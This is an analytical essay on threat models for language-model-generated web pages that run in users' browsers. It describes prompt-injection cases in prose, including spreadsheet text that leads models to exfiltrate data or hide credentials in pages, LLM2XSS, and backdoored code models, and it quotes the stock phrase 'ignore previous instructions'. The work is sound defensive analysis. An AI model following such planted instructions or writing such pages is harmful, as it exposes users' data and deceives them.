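# Threat models for systems in which a language model writes code that runs in the user's browser

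## From a request in words to code running in the browser

In several chat products, a language model can now answer a request in ordinary words by writing a web page, a chart or a small tool, which the user's browser runs at once. Such a program is a *generated page*. It uses HTML for structure, JavaScript for behaviour, and sometimes WebAssembly, a binary format that lets browsers run code written in other languages, such as Python. Anthropic, the company behind the Claude models, calls its generated pages artifacts, and Anthropic's *What are artifacts and how do I use them?* lists designs, documents, dashboards and small interactive tools as examples. OpenAI's ChatGPT has a comparable side panel called Canvas.

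People tend to like the interfaces that models generate. In *Generative Interfaces for Language Models*, Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2025) recruited 428 annotators to compare generated interfaces with ordinary chat answers on 100 requests. When Claude 3.7 produced both, annotators preferred the interface on 84% of requests and the text on 12%. The preference for interfaces was strongest in data analysis and visualisation, at 93.8%. A product that dropped generated code for safety would therefore lose something its users want.

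In an ordinary case, an employee uploads a spreadsheet of the year's expenses to a chat product and asks for an interactive chart of spending by department. The spreadsheet contains names, dates, amounts and descriptions copied from suppliers' invoices. A chart with working filters appears in a panel beside the conversation. A week later, she sends her colleagues a link to the chart.

### What a threat model records

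A threat model is a written account of how a system can come to harm. It lists the assets worth protecting, the adversaries and what each can do, the parts of the system the analyst trusts, and the consequences if an attack succeeds or that trust is misplaced. It need not be complete. MDN's *Threat modeling*, a tutorial for web developers, describes the exercise as a way to improve understanding over time.

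The draft *Threat Modeling Guide* (2026) from the World Wide Web Consortium (W3C), a web standards body, defines a trust boundary as the place where different authorities, privileges or responsibilities meet. Threats often appear where something crosses such a boundary, so the guide recommends drawing the flow of data first and adding the boundaries afterwards. It also recommends asking who is harmed when something goes wrong. With generated pages, that can be someone who never made a request.

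A threat model depends heavily on its assumptions, and a good one states them openly. *Beware EviLLM* (2026), which studies attacks that insert vulnerabilities into code written by ChatGPT, assumes a victim who deploys the code with little review and an honest provider whose platform may not stop someone from tampering with the account or the browser. It excludes attackers who break into the provider's infrastructure or intercept encrypted traffic, on the grounds that they would need far greater capabilities. Those limits are fair for a study of one attack, but they would be too narrow for the expenses chart, because the employee's firm may send its traffic through an intermediary that reads everything without breaking any encryption.

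The obvious asset in the expenses case is the spreadsheet. An attacker may want to read or alter its rows, and a chart with false totals does damage even if nothing leaks. Another asset is the login session, the cookie or token that identifies the employee to the chat product's server. A thief who holds it could open her other conversations. Her account may also be connected to other services. According to Anthropic, artifacts can read from and write to Asana, Google Calendar and Slack once the user approves. Her colleagues' trust is an asset too, since they will open the link because she sent it. So is the device, with its files, camera and processor. W3C's draft threat model for the web as a whole adds the private network around the device, through which a browser inside an office can reach printers and internal servers closed to the outside world.

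### The stages between request and screen

The code passes through up to eight stages, and control changes hands at nearly every one.

| Stage | What goes in | What comes out | Who controls it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Request and data | The employee's words and the spreadsheet | A prompt for the model | The employee, and anyone who wrote text in the spreadsheet |
| Model | The prompt | The source code of a page | The company that trained the model |
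| Provider's server | The source code | A stored page or a reply | The provider |
| Relay (optional) | Requests and replies | The same, altered or not | The employer, a reseller or another operator |
| Verifier (optional) | The source code | Acceptance or rejection | The product's developer |
| Host page | The accepted code | A frame that contains the code | The product's developer |
| Sandboxed frame | The code and the rows it displays | The chart, and requests to the host page | The generated code, within the browser's limits |
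| Sharing | A link | The same code in other people's browsers | The employee and her firm's administrators |

**Request and data.** The employee wrote the request, but suppliers wrote the invoice descriptions, and the model receives both in the same stream of text. A supplier could therefore put a *planted instruction* in a description, which is a sentence meant to change what the model does. This technique is usually called prompt injection. Some systems have other channels for planted instructions. The one Chen and colleagues built also searches the web for example interfaces and data sources, and passes what it finds to the model.

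In the simplest products, the model writes the page in one go. In Chen and colleagues' system, the model first writes a specification of what the user needs, then a map of the screens and a description of how each component changes state when the user clicks, and only then the HTML, CSS and JavaScript. A model scores several candidate pages out of 100, and the system regenerates the page from the best one until a candidate reaches 90 or five rounds have passed. The scoring criteria concern things like clarity and visual structure, so a page that looks excellent but leaks its data could still score very well.

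The provider's server stores the page and gives it an address, but it may not check the page's content. The security company Pluto Security tested this on Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code, by placing a proxy between the agent and Anthropic's servers. *Inside Claude Artifacts*, the company's report, says that the server enforced permissions strictly. It rejected any request with an unfamiliar field, and an agent had no way to make a page public. But when the testers replaced the page's HTML with their own in transit, the server accepted and served it.

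A **relay** passes requests and answers between the user's software and the model provider. An employer may run one to control costs or keep records, and a reseller may run one to offer many models through a single account. *LLM in the Middle* (2025), a review of threats to systems built on language models, describes an adversary who impersonates the provider's server, reads sensitive content and changes the data on its way to the application. The operator of an ordinary relay is already in a position to read and change this data, because the user's software is set up to send its requests through the relay.

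A **verifier** is any component that accepts or rejects generated code before it runs. It can be a simple check that the output has the expected form, a second model that reads the code, or a program that checks mathematical proofs. *Djinnlang* (Henniger, Chong and Amin, 2026) describes a strict system in which a person writes only a specification. A conventional translator turns the specification into statements that need proof, a language model writes both the program and the proofs, and the checker for the programming language Dafny accepts or rejects them. If the checker rejects them, its error messages go back to the model for another attempt. The specification, translator and checker must be trustworthy, but the model need not be. Many generated pages run without any verifier, and Pluto Security found no content check between Claude Code and the browser.

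The **host page** is the product's own page, in this case the chat window, and it holds the employee's login. How much an unknown program can do on that page depends on a few rules that browsers share.

An *origin* is the combination of scheme, host name and port in a page's address. Pages from `chat.example` and `pages.example` have different origins, and so do two pages from the same host if one came over http and the other over https. Under the *same-origin rule*, the browser's central security rule, a script can read pages and stored data only from its own origin, with a few controlled exceptions. This keeps a game in one tab from reading a bank balance in another. The rule restricts reading much more than sending, though. A script can request an image from almost any server and put stolen data in the image's address, and the server's owner can then find the data in a log. Moving a victim's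 data to a place the attacker can read is called *exfiltration*.

*Cross-site scripting* (XSS) is the classic way around the same-origin rule. The attacker gets a script into a page that the victim trusts, for instance by posting a comment that contains code on a site that doesn't filter comments. The browser can't tell the attacker's script from the site's own, so the script runs with the site's origin and can act as the logged-in victim. *Shifting from Injection to Interaction* (Singh, Abuadbba and colleagues, 2026) cites the standard definition of the flaw, "improper neutralization of input during web page generation", and argues that a language model can become a conduit for such attacks by turning a stranger's text into a harmful script. Unlike an ordinary website, where a foreign script is a mistake, a product that generates pages is built to run code that nobody has read. Its developer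 can't keep such scripts out and so has to give them an origin where there is little to steal.

**Sandboxed frame.** A frame is a page inside another page, and a *sandboxed frame* is one whose abilities the browser has restricted. *How Anthropic built Artifacts*, by the programmer Simon Willison, excerpts a 2024 interview in which Anthropic's engineers described the first version of artifacts. They said they ran each artifact in a sandboxed frame, in a separate browser process, to protect the user's main session. Pluto Security later found that each web artifact also had its own origin, so two artifacts could not read each other's data.

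A frame alone does not stop code from sending data out through an image address. To block this, a developer adds a *content security policy* (CSP), a list of rules that tells the browser where a page may load code from and which servers it may contact. Pluto Security built a test artifact that tried to send data out by five routes, including an image request, and the browser blocked all five. Anthropic's policy now deliberately allows artifacts to load script libraries from five outside hosts and fonts from Google. Generated code cannot disable the policy by deleting it. *Can JavaScript Escape a CSP Meta Tag Inside an Iframe?* (Willison, 2026) reports that, in tests on Chromium and Firefox, a policy written at the top of a framed page stayed in force after scripts removed or edited it.

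A chart isolated in this way could show only the data it came with. To get live figures, it needs a *bridge*, a channel for sending requests to the host page. In Anthropic's version, the generated page sends a message and the chat product makes the call through the viewer's own account, so the page never receives a password or token. The viewer must approve before the first call. The bridge can also carry out actions, since a button on the page may post a message or update a record in the viewer's name. Keeping the credentials from the page therefore protects them from theft, but the page could still misuse the access they provide.

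**Sharing.** Artifacts start private, and a link opens them to others. The link can expose more than the sender expects. Artifacts made in a Claude chat before 16 September 2026 follow older rules, and Anthropic's *Share artifacts* warns that, on plans for firms, anyone who can view such an artifact can also access the files attached to the chat. The employee who meant to show her colleagues departmental totals would have given them access to the whole spreadsheet, without any attacker being involved. Pages can also change after people have opened them. According to Anthropic, Claude Code republishes a page to the same address and open copies update in place, though the author can choose which version viewers see. A colleague who has already checked the chart may therefore later run code that she hasn't checked.

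### Why the code runs on the user's machine

The same chart could come from a server. NVIDIA's *Sandboxing Agentic AI Workflows with WebAssembly* compares running a model's Python charting code on a server and in the browser. In the server design, the user asks for a chart, the application adds context and passes the request to the model, the model returns Python code, and the server runs the code and sends back the plot. If the code is malicious, it runs on a machine that all users share, so it may compromise the application, the operating system and other users' data. Filtering the code is a weak remedy because a rule that blocks Python's `os` module, which gives access to the system, may miss `subprocess`, which starts other programs. Running each job in its own small virtual machine gives stronger protection but takes computing resources and engineering time.

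In the browser design, the server returns a page containing the model's code and Pyodide, a version of Python compiled to WebAssembly. The user's browser then runs the code, and the server executes none of it. Malicious code either fails because a module it needs is missing or runs inside the browser's sandbox on one person's device. This saves the provider computing power, and the code cannot reach its other customers.

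NVIDIA presents this as an improvement for the user too, and it is one compared with careless execution on a shared server. But if a well-isolated server draws the chart and sends back a plain image, no generated code enters the user's browser. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes that arrangement for the code Claude runs during a chat, which executes in a temporary container on the company's own machines. Since users' machines are not exposed, it says, the task is to protect the infrastructure and to protect customers from one another. Moving execution into the browser removes a risk for the provider and creates one for the user, in exchange for a chart that responds to clicks.

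Moving execution from the server to the browser can also remove a defence by accident. In December 2024, ChatGPT's older Code Interpreter ran Python on OpenAI's servers with no network access, while its new Canvas feature ran Python in the browser and could contact outside servers that accepted its requests. Willison (2024), in *ChatGPT Canvas can make API requests now, but it’s complicated*, pointed out that a planted instruction might cause the model to write Canvas code that sent private material from the conversation to an attacker. He did not build the attack, and OpenAI showed a warning before the code ran, but users who knew Code Interpreter had little reason to expect that Canvas code could access the network.

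### Four deployments

How much a bad program can reach depends heavily on where the product puts it. The least risky arrangement is a *private preview*, where only the employee sees the chart. Nobody else can attack her through it or be harmed by it, but the code still handles her spreadsheet and may have a bridge to her accounts. It may also run before she has a chance to look at it. For example, when Claude Code publishes a new artifact in response to a typed request, it does so without asking for separate permission, and the browser opens the page automatically.

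A *shared page* is made by one person and run by another, so a dishonest author could use it against the person who runs it. The risk depends largely on whose accounts the bridge uses. Pluto Security had a colleague without a calendar connection open an artifact that requested calendar data. The colleague got a refusal and an offer to connect a calendar, but no access to the author's calendar. This protects authors from viewers, but it does less to protect viewers, because the bridge uses their own accounts once they approve. Anthropic tells viewers to treat another person's artifact like a file from an unknown sender. Someone outside the author's organisation who opens a public link gets the page without its live connections.

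Some developers skip the frame and put the generated code directly into the host page, which is less work and lets the chart match the surrounding design. The code then shares an origin with the login, so any hostile script in it has the powers of an XSS attack. Google Cloud's *What is Generative UI?* names XSS as a significant risk when a model produces raw code for display, and contrasts this with designs where the model can only choose from prepared components. WebAssembly does not remove the danger, because Pyodide lets Python code call the JavaScript of the surrounding page. A Python program in the host page may therefore still reach the employee's session, even though it is isolated from the operating system.

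A *generated browser extension* can have even wider access. The user installs it in the browser, and with the right permissions it can work across many sites and read cookies, history and bookmarks. Chrome divides an extension into scripts that touch web pages, which have few privileges, and background scripts, which have many. The two communicate by messages. If the background script acts on messages without checking them, a hostile web page can use its privileges. In *When AI Takes the Wheel*, Liu, Pan and colleagues (2025) asked nine models from 2024 and early 2025 to write extensions for 140 descriptions, with a general instruction to make them secure. Between 18% and 50% of the results were vulnerable, depending on the model, and most of the flaws exposed cookies, history or bookmarks to untrusted code. These figures call for caution because the researchers based their descriptions on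 extensions already known to be vulnerable, looked for dangerous data flows without trying to exploit them, and used models that are now well out of date. But the underlying problem remains that no frame or separate origin stands between an extension and the sites it has permission to read.

### Four failures

In all these deployments, four failures can turn the expenses chart into an attack. In *malicious model output*, the model writes harmful code even though the employee and the provider are both honest. The cause may be a planted instruction or a *backdoor*, a behaviour trained into the model that appears only when a particular trigger is present. A *malicious user* makes a hostile page on purpose and sends it to others. A *compromised server* (or relay) replaces good code with bad after the model has finished. In a *verifier failure*, a check passes a program that it should have stopped.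 Anthropic similarly divides the risks of its own products into misuse by users, misbehaviour by the model and attacks from outside.

Verifier failure differs from the other three because a verifier writes no code. It does harm only when someone or something supplies a bad program and the verifier approves it. A verifier that wrongly rejects good charts is a nuisance, but it doesn't endanger anyone's data. Verifiers still matter because people stop reading code once they believe a machine has checked it. Henniger and colleagues concede that if their verifier fails, the user has no protection from a model that nobody supervises any longer.

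A verifier's coverage depends on where it runs. A verifier on the provider's server can catch bad output from the model, but not changes that a relay makes to the code afterwards. One that runs in the host page, just before the code enters the frame, can catch both, provided that the server that delivers the host page is trustworthy.

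## Instructions planted in what the model reads

A supplier with no account on the chat product and no access to its servers can still change the code of the expenses chart, because the model reads the supplier's invoice descriptions together with the employee's request. *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (2026) traces this weakness to the model's input, which lacks the strict separation of code and data that conventional software enforces. The model has to infer from wording and position which sentences are instructions, and a well-written invoice line can mislead it.

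### How outside text gets in

*AI in Excel and Google Sheets*, a guide from the security company PromptArmor, lists the usual ways other people's text gets into a spreadsheet: reference tables copied from the web, vendors' templates, exports from software with free-text fields that customers or job candidates fill in, and integrations that turn incoming emails into rows. Attackers typically hide their instructions, for instance in white letters on a white cell, so that the employee doesn't notice the text but the model still reads it. A product that searches the web for examples also takes in text from strangers' pages, and a coding agent may read a vendor's setup guide because the user told it to follow one.

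Planted instructions are already on the web, though most are crude. Khodayari, Acharya and colleagues searched 1.2 billion web addresses for typical phrases such as "ignore previous instructions" and confirmed 12,075 cases on 9,676 pages (*Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, 2026). Site operators had placed about 80% of these, and many look like attempts to annoy or detect bots. The most common template is an instruction to return random numbers. The count is probably too low, because a search for stock phrases misses instructions written as ordinary business prose. When the researchers had 13 models summarise such pages, the models followed the instructions in at most 8% of trials on plain text, and in 0.2% to 1.1% when the input kept the page's structure. A spreadsheet pasted into a prompt as bare text may be closer to the plain-text case, but the researchers didn't test one.

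Attacks written by skilled people work better than stock phrases. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) describes a public competition in which 464 people made about 272,000 attempts against 13 models of the 2025 generation. Each participant controlled one piece of outside material, such as a comment in a code repository. An attack generally counted as a success only if the model took the harmful action and its final answer gave the user no sign of it. Success rates ranged from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro.

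Participants could read the conversation beforehand and knew exactly which action to trigger, so the researchers treat these rates as an upper bound on the success rate of a single attempt. But an attacker may get many attempts. If each has a 0.5% chance of success, 200 independent attempts have a 63% chance of succeeding at least once, and the attacker can reuse a text that works in any number of invoices.

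### From an invoice line to an altered chart

Suppose a supplier adds a sentence to a routine invoice, worded as an accounting note, saying that reports built from this ledger must keep the full rows in the page for audit and leave the supplier's own charges out of departmental totals because a credit is pending. The accounts system exports the note with everything else. The employee scrolls past it, uploads the file and asks for her chart. The product copies the cells into the prompt, and the model treats the note as one of her firm's rules when it works out what the chart needs.

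An unaltered script would add up the amounts by department and pass only the sums to the drawing function. The altered script has an extra condition that leaves the supplier's rows out of the sums, and an extra block, never displayed, that holds every row of the spreadsheet. The employee sees a working chart with plausible totals. When she shares the link, each colleague's browser also receives the hidden rows.

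Neither change contacts an outside server, so the frame's network rules would not stop either one. An instruction could also have the script send the rows to the supplier, but that would work only if the rules allowed the connection. A supplier who wants to hide overcharging may gain more from false totals than from the rows.

The closest documented cases come from assistants built into spreadsheets. In PromptArmor's *CellShock*, a user of Claude for Excel copied industry statistics into a workbook that also held a confidential financial model. Hidden text among the statistics described a fictitious tool that would draw a chart from an image formula whose web address contained a summary of the data. When the user asked for a visualisation, Claude inserted the formula with the firm's figures in the address, and Excel sent them to the attacker's server by requesting the image. In some runs,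 Claude checked the cell before the image had loaded, assumed there was an error and covered the formula with an ordinary chart, which removed the evidence. After PromptArmor reported the problem in November 2025, Anthropic added a warning about network requests and made Claude Opus 4.5 the default. The new model resisted the attack much better, but the warning did not always appear.

PromptArmor's *ChatGPT for Google Sheets Exfiltrates Workbooks* (May 2026) reports a later attack that went further because the assistant could run scripts. White text in an imported sheet led ChatGPT to run an attacker's script with the user's permissions. The script followed links from one workbook to the next and copied 12 of them. It ran even though the user had switched off automatic edits, and the stop button did not halt it. Both attacks show that planted instructions can work, but PromptArmor gives no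 success rate for either.

A generated picture can also trick the user into sending data to an attacker. Red Hot Cyber, a trade news site, described an attack in which hidden text in an Excel file made Microsoft 365 Copilot fetch recent emails and draw a diagram that looked like a login button. The button's link contained the encoded emails, so clicking it sent them to the attacker. According to daily.dev's summary, Microsoft fixed this by making such diagrams non-interactive. That fix is reasonable for a flowchart, but it would remove the filters from the expenses chart.

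### When the host page runs what it meant to display

In all these cases, the model was supposed to produce a formula, script or drawing, and it produced a harmful one. Chat products that are only supposed to display an answer can fail in a different way. The model's reply contains markup, the host page inserts it without neutralising it, and the browser runs it as part of the page. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian (2026), in *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation*, call this LLM2XSS. They treat it as an old flaw, cross-site scripting, with the model giving the attacker a new way to deliver the script.

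In a documented example from the DeepSeek chat site, an attacker's prompt contained an encoded string and an instruction to decode it and print only the result. The result was markup with a script that read the user's login token and cookies, and the chat page ran the script. If a product saves such a reply and later shows it to somebody else, the script runs in that person's session.

Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian did not measure how often LLM2XSS succeeds, leaving that to future work. They tested a related attack, server-side request forgery, in which the attacker gets a server to fetch an internal address that outsiders can't reach. They built a single test application, a concert assistant called TicketOracle, whose model could fetch any web address. In April 2026 they tried five attack scenarios on seven models, with ten trials of each. Typing the attack into the chat worked at least once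 on five models and never on GPT-5.2 or Claude Opus 4.6.

The scenario that most resembles a planted cell used a concert review containing a fake system notice. An ordinary user then asked what people thought of the concert. Llama 3.3 70B followed the notice in 6 of 10 trials, GPT-oss 120B in 5, and the other five models in none. The researchers then added a list of permitted addresses to the model's instructions and changed the review to claim that the list now included the internal address. With these changes, Llama followed the notice in 10 trials and GPT-oss in none.

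These results are weak evidence about rates. All ten trials of a scenario took place in one conversation, where a model that has complied or refused once is likely to do the same again. The attack also changed along with the defence, so the results don't show that the list caused Llama's rise. The useful finding is that a written rule stopped one model from complying and failed completely with another.

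Better evidence for LLM2XSS itself comes from security companies' work on real products. Quarkslab attacked a customer's live system and later rebuilt the attack around a mock medical assistant. The testers told the chatbot to end its answer with a frame containing a script, and the page ran the script. Any logged-in user could open another user's conversation by its address, so an attacker could take over the platform by getting an administrator to click one link. Escape, which sells automated security testing, found the same flaw at two unrelated companies within weeks. Both displayed the model's Markdown, a simple notation for tables and links, with raw HTML switched on and no filter to remove dangerous parts.

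In those tests the attacker typed into a chat, but an attacker can also plant instructions in text the model reads. Escape cites a flaw in NoteGen, a desktop program with an AI chat, where instructions in a malicious reference file led the model to emit HTML that ran with the program's privileges. In a training exercise from PortSwigger, which teaches web security, students plant a product review that the model repeats word for word. When another customer asks about the product, the repeated text deletes that customer's account.

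The two failures need different remedies. A page that only displays answers can convert all markup to plain text or allow only a short list of harmless elements. Escape points out that most teams can do this by removing one add-on, and that tables, links and code samples still work afterwards. The expenses chart can't be fixed this way, because the code is what the employee asked for.

### Pluto Security's integration guide

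Pluto Security, the company that swapped a page's HTML on its way to Anthropic's server, also tried to get the model itself to write a harmful page. Its testers asked an agent to build a status page by following a vendor's integration guide, which they had written in the tone of company policy and served from a realistic vendor address. Nothing in the guide was addressed to an AI, but it called for the page to include values from the user's local settings in a hidden element.

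The settings were in `.env.local`, a file where developers often keep passwords and access keys. The testers had filled it with synthetic credentials. They ran the same task 145 times and report that in 10 of 85 attempts, the agent copied the file's contents into a script block that never shows on screen and published the page. Anthropic's server accepted one such page that held six credentials.

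Ten of 85 is about 12%, with a 95% confidence interval of roughly 6.5% to 20%. That interval accounts only for chance variation between similar runs. Pluto Security doesn't explain what happened in the other 60 runs, and if they were failed attempts of the same kind, the rate would be about 7%. It also doesn't name the models, though it says the more capable ones followed their rules better. As a security vendor, it has a commercial interest in finding problems. The result is good evidence that a plain business document can do this, but it gives only a rough estimate of how often it happens.

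The figure measures exposure rather than theft. The page started out private, and the frame's rules stopped it from sending anything out, so an attacker would have to get the page itself. That could easily happen if the user sent the link to the vendor for help with the integration. Anthropic's content rules for the model did not cover this case. They forbid impersonation, fabricated records and deceptive forms that collect passwords, which protects the people who open a page but not the secrets of the person who makes it.

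The user did have a chance to stop it. In Cowork, an Anthropic product that builds artifacts in its desktop app, the user must click Create or Cancel, but the model writes the description in that prompt. On a run where it had hidden the secrets, it described a page showing the status of core services, "built per StatusKit integration guide", and didn't mention credentials. The description was accurate but incomplete. The model had mistaken the hidden block for part of the vendor's specification, so it didn't single it out. The user was therefore asked to judge the page from a summary written by the model, which the attacker had already influenced.

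Claude for Excel had a similar weakness in the CellShock attack, where the approval box read "Add visualization" and left out the address. Attackers can also aim for a misleading summary, as Dziemian and colleagues' participants did in thousands of successful attacks. An approval prompt would be more useful if ordinary software compiled it from the page's source, for example by listing the local files whose contents appear there. This would help only when a prompt appears, and Pluto Security counted 28 pages published without one in a session where settings let the agent publish freely.

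### Writing the program before reading the data

Better training and second-model reviewers may lower these rates, but both still rely on a model recognising an attack. The main structural defence is to have the model write the program first, so that only the finished program handles untrusted text. *Securing Web Agents with the Compile-Then-Execute Paradigm* (Chow, Zhu and colleagues, 2026) presents Baya, a system built this way. Baya carries out tasks on websites, but the same reasoning applies to systems that draw pages.

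Baya's model sees the user's request and a catalogue of the operations a website offers, such as searching for products or posting a comment. It writes a Python program and tests it on made-up responses, with no access to the live site. A separate process then runs the program. If the program fails, the model gets an error message, which must not contain any content from the site, and may revise the program up to three times. A planted review can supply a value or affect which existing branch the program takes, but it can't add an operation to the program.

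The expenses chart suits this order well. To write the script, the model needs the employee's request and the column names, but not the invoice descriptions. The browser later passes the rows to the finished script, which treats the supplier's note as a string of characters. The column names must still come from someone the firm trusts, and the script must display descriptions as text. Otherwise, a supplier could put markup in a description and attack the page without involving the model.

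Some requests need a model to read the data, such as grouping an employee's expenses by what the descriptions mean. Baya lets a program call a model at run time for this. The model has no tools and returns only a value, so a planted note could put an expense in the wrong group but could not rewrite the chart. Of 627 programs, 13 contained such a call and 11 (1.8%) made it. In the other 616, no model read the site's content.

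Chow and colleagues tested Baya with three models on 84 planted attacks, and none led it to take a first step towards the attacker's goal. Agents that chose each action after reading the page took such a step in 16% to 26% of cases, depending on their tools, though they almost never completed the attack. The design matters more than the count, because an attack that never reaches the planner can't influence its plan. Baya also completed 77.8% of ordinary tasks, compared with 66.7% for an agent with the same website operations, but it took 327 seconds per task rather than 87 and cost about twice as much. The researchers had to prepare each site's catalogue by hand.

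The zero does not cover what Chow and colleagues call outcome manipulation, where false data leads a correct program to a wrong result. The protection therefore doesn't stop a supplier from distorting the chart by misstating an amount.

This order of work also rules out every task whose steps have to come from the untrusted material. Chow and colleagues give the example of an assistant told to find an email from the boss and do whatever it says. According to an earlier classification they cite, their benchmark contains no such tasks, so their results can't be used to estimate how often users would run into this limit. People who ask for generated pages might run into it fairly often. The model has to read before it writes if it is asked to rebuild a dashboard from a written description, correct a page according to comments in a shared file, copy the layout of an example found on the web,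 or follow a vendor's integration guide, as in Pluto Security's trial. Chow and colleagues propose handing control back to the user in such cases. A user with an integration guide would then have to read it and state its requirements herself.

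## Harmful code from the model itself

A model can also write harmful code when nothing it reads is malicious. It may make a mistake, or someone may have tampered with its training so that it writes bad code in response to a particular cue. It may also pursue its task by means that the user never asked for and wouldn't accept. Any of these could leave the same flaw in a page, such as a login token stored where others can read it, but they differ in what an attacker must do beforehand, how often harm appears and whether testing would find it.

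### Ordinary errors

A model can write a flawed page without being attacked. An attacker can then exploit the flaw, and often needs to control only an input to the finished page, such as a comment, a link or an invoice description that the expenses chart displays as HTML.

Andročec (2026), in *The Effect of Security-Focused Prompts on Reported Findings*, measured how many flaws current coding agents leave in web applications and how much it helps to ask for security. Two agents, Anthropic's Claude Code with Opus 4.8 and OpenAI's Codex CLI with GPT-5.5, built applications from 100 specifications, ranging from a form that greets the user by name to platforms with several user roles. Each agent built every application twice, once from the specification alone and once with an added paragraph that required, among other things, validated input, encoded output to prevent XSS, hashed passwords and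 no secrets in the code. The same automatic scanners examined all 400 applications.

For either agent, the scanners reported about 20 findings per application without the paragraph and 13 to 14 with it. After adjustment for agent, language and task complexity, the reduction was 35% (95% confidence interval 29% to 40%). Andročec did not confirm that anyone could exploit the reported flaws. Most of the reduction was in findings such as missing security headers and cookie settings, which a chat product usually controls itself for the pages it hosts, so high-severity findings in the applications' own source code are a better guide to generated pages. Those fell from 103 to 54, or from about one for every two applications to about one for every four.

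The security paragraph also roughly doubled the number of outside packages that the applications declared, and high-severity warnings about those packages rose from 198 to 344. The rise came from the larger number of packages, since the rate of warnings per package stayed about the same. Some of the added packages served no purpose. Among 38 pairs of applications whose specifications mentioned no users or accounts, 36 of the versions with the paragraph included a login or session package, compared with 17 of those without it. The packages behind most of the new warnings run on servers, so a chart that runs entirely in the browser wouldn't contain them. A model might still respond to a request for security by loading a script library that the chart doesn't need, and the employee would then be trusting that code too.

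The experiment cannot separate the effect of the security wording from that of a longer prompt, because no prompt had a neutral paragraph of the same length in its place. Each agent also built each version only once.

Andročec's earlier *Vibe Coding and Web Application Security* (2026) found that scanners miss some serious flaws. Opus 4.8 built each of six applications twice, once with a section of security requirements and once without. Andročec reviewed 85 candidate findings individually, and 75 were real, with 51 in the versions without the requirements and 24 in the versions with them. All 13 flaws of critical or high severity were in the versions without the requirements. The worst was a secret key written into the code of a task manager, which let an attacker forge any user's login token. Manual testing confirmed this attack, but no scanner had reported it as an attack.

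Only 12 of the 75 flaws turned up in more than one kind of test, so a clean result from a single scanner means little. The study is weak evidence about prompts, because the model generated each of the 12 programs only once and one person judged them. In the larger experiment, high-severity problems remained in applications built with security instructions, which corrects one of the study's findings.

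*Understanding the (In)Security of Vibe-Coded Applications* (Deng, Fan and Meng, 2026) examined applications that people had put online, whereas both earlier studies used specifications written for research. "Vibe coding" means describing an application to an AI agent and leaving most of the design and programming to it. The researchers collected 9,041 open-source projects in which Claude Code or the app builder Lovable had written at least 90% of the code, and sampled 200 that were publicly deployed. Two AI agents, each working with two sets of auditing instructions, searched every application for flaws. Another agent then tried to build a harmless test attack for each candidate flaw, and two of the researchers reviewed the remaining cases. They confirmed 1,186 flaws from 11,150 raw reports. Of the 200 applications, 182 (91%) had at least one confirmed flaw.

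That percentage doesn't apply to the expenses chart. About 53% of the flaws were in server code and 11% in configuration, and a simple generated page may have no server code or configuration. The other 426 flaws (36%) were in code that runs in the browser, including 95 injection flaws, the category that contains XSS. Applications with more than 20,000 lines of code had about 12 flaws each, while the 15 smallest, with 5,000 lines or fewer, had about two. A chart of a few hundred lines would probably have even fewer, although the small applications had more flaws per line.

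A request for something quick can produce insecure code. In one of the browser flaws, an application stored users' access tokens in the browser after "encrypting" them with base64, an encoding that anyone can reverse, and a comment in the code said this was for a demo. Deng and colleagues attribute 174 flaws (15%) to designs that, like this one, put a working demonstration ahead of security. Generated pages seem especially prone to this problem because their users generally want to see something work immediately.

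The range of 18% to 50% for browser extensions, from Liu and colleagues, is the share of their 140 descriptions for which at least one of up to 12 attempts produced a vulnerable extension. Vulnerable extensions made up only about 6% to 17% of the 1,680 attempts per model. GPT-4o, for example, produced 115 flawed extensions from 41 descriptions, an average of about three in every 12 attempts at those descriptions. The same request can therefore give a safe program on one attempt and a flawed one on the next, so testing one result is weak evidence about another. Extensions that handled logins or cookies did worst. Liu and colleagues also conclude that reasoning models produce more flaws, but their data are mixed, since a reasoning model, Gemini 2.0 Flash Thinking, had the lowest rate of the nine models.

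Veracode, which sells code scanning and so has a commercial interest in such results, reported a higher rate per program. According to Andročec's earlier study, Veracode tested more than 100 models on 80 coding tasks in 2025 and found that about 45% of the samples introduced a weakness from the OWASP Top 10, a standard list of common web security risks. The studies' rates differ widely mainly because they measure different things. A large application has many more places for a flaw than a short extension does, and a task chosen to prompt a particular mistake will produce it more often than an everyday request.

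### Private and shared pages

Many of these flaws are harmless while only the employee opens the chart, but sharing the chart can make them dangerous even if the code doesn't change.

| Flaw in the chart | Only the employee opens it | Other people open it |
|---|---|---|
| It displays outside text as HTML | Dangerous if someone else wrote the text, as with invoice descriptions | Dangerous to every viewer, and viewers may be able to add hostile text themselves |
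| Its source contains a password or access key | Little risk while the page stays private | Every viewer can read the secret |
| Its own script checks who may see which rows | No effect, because she may see all of them | Any viewer can bypass the check and read the hidden rows |
| It calculates a total wrongly | Misleads her | Misleads everyone who relies on it |

The model can easily make a mistake in the check on who may see which rows. The employee might ask for a chart in which each manager sees only one department, and the model might send all the rows to every browser and hide most of them with a script. The chart would look right, but a manager who opened the page's source could read the whole spreadsheet. If the employee tried the chart only from her own account, she would find nothing wrong. A useful test would be to open the page as one of the managers and inspect the data the browser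 receives as well as what appears on the screen.

### Backdoors and poisoned training data

A backdoor makes harmful code deliberately rare, because the backdoor stays dormant until its trigger appears. The idea predates language models. In 1984 the computer scientist Ken Thompson described an attack on a compiler, the program that turns source code into machine instructions. Thompson's compiler added a secret way in whenever it compiled the system's login program. It also copied this behaviour into any new version of the compiler it compiled. A programmer could read the source code of both programs and find nothing wrong, because the malicious code existed only in the compiled compiler.

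McDanel (2025), in *Beyond Trusting Trust*, applies the comparison to models that write code and argues that they are harder to inspect than compilers. Malicious instructions in a compiler follow fixed logic, and an analyst can find them by studying the compiled program. A model's behaviour comes from vast numbers of weights acting together, and McDanel thinks that finding a hidden rule by examining them is currently infeasible. The trigger can also be as subtle as a copyright notice or an author's name, which a tester has no reason to try.

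A backdoored model writes its harmful code into the page's source, where anyone can read it. This gives the defender one advantage over Thompson's victims, who had clean source code but a bad compiled program. The attack relies on people not reading generated code. McDanel points out that even someone who did read it might dismiss the flaw as a hallucination or poor programming.

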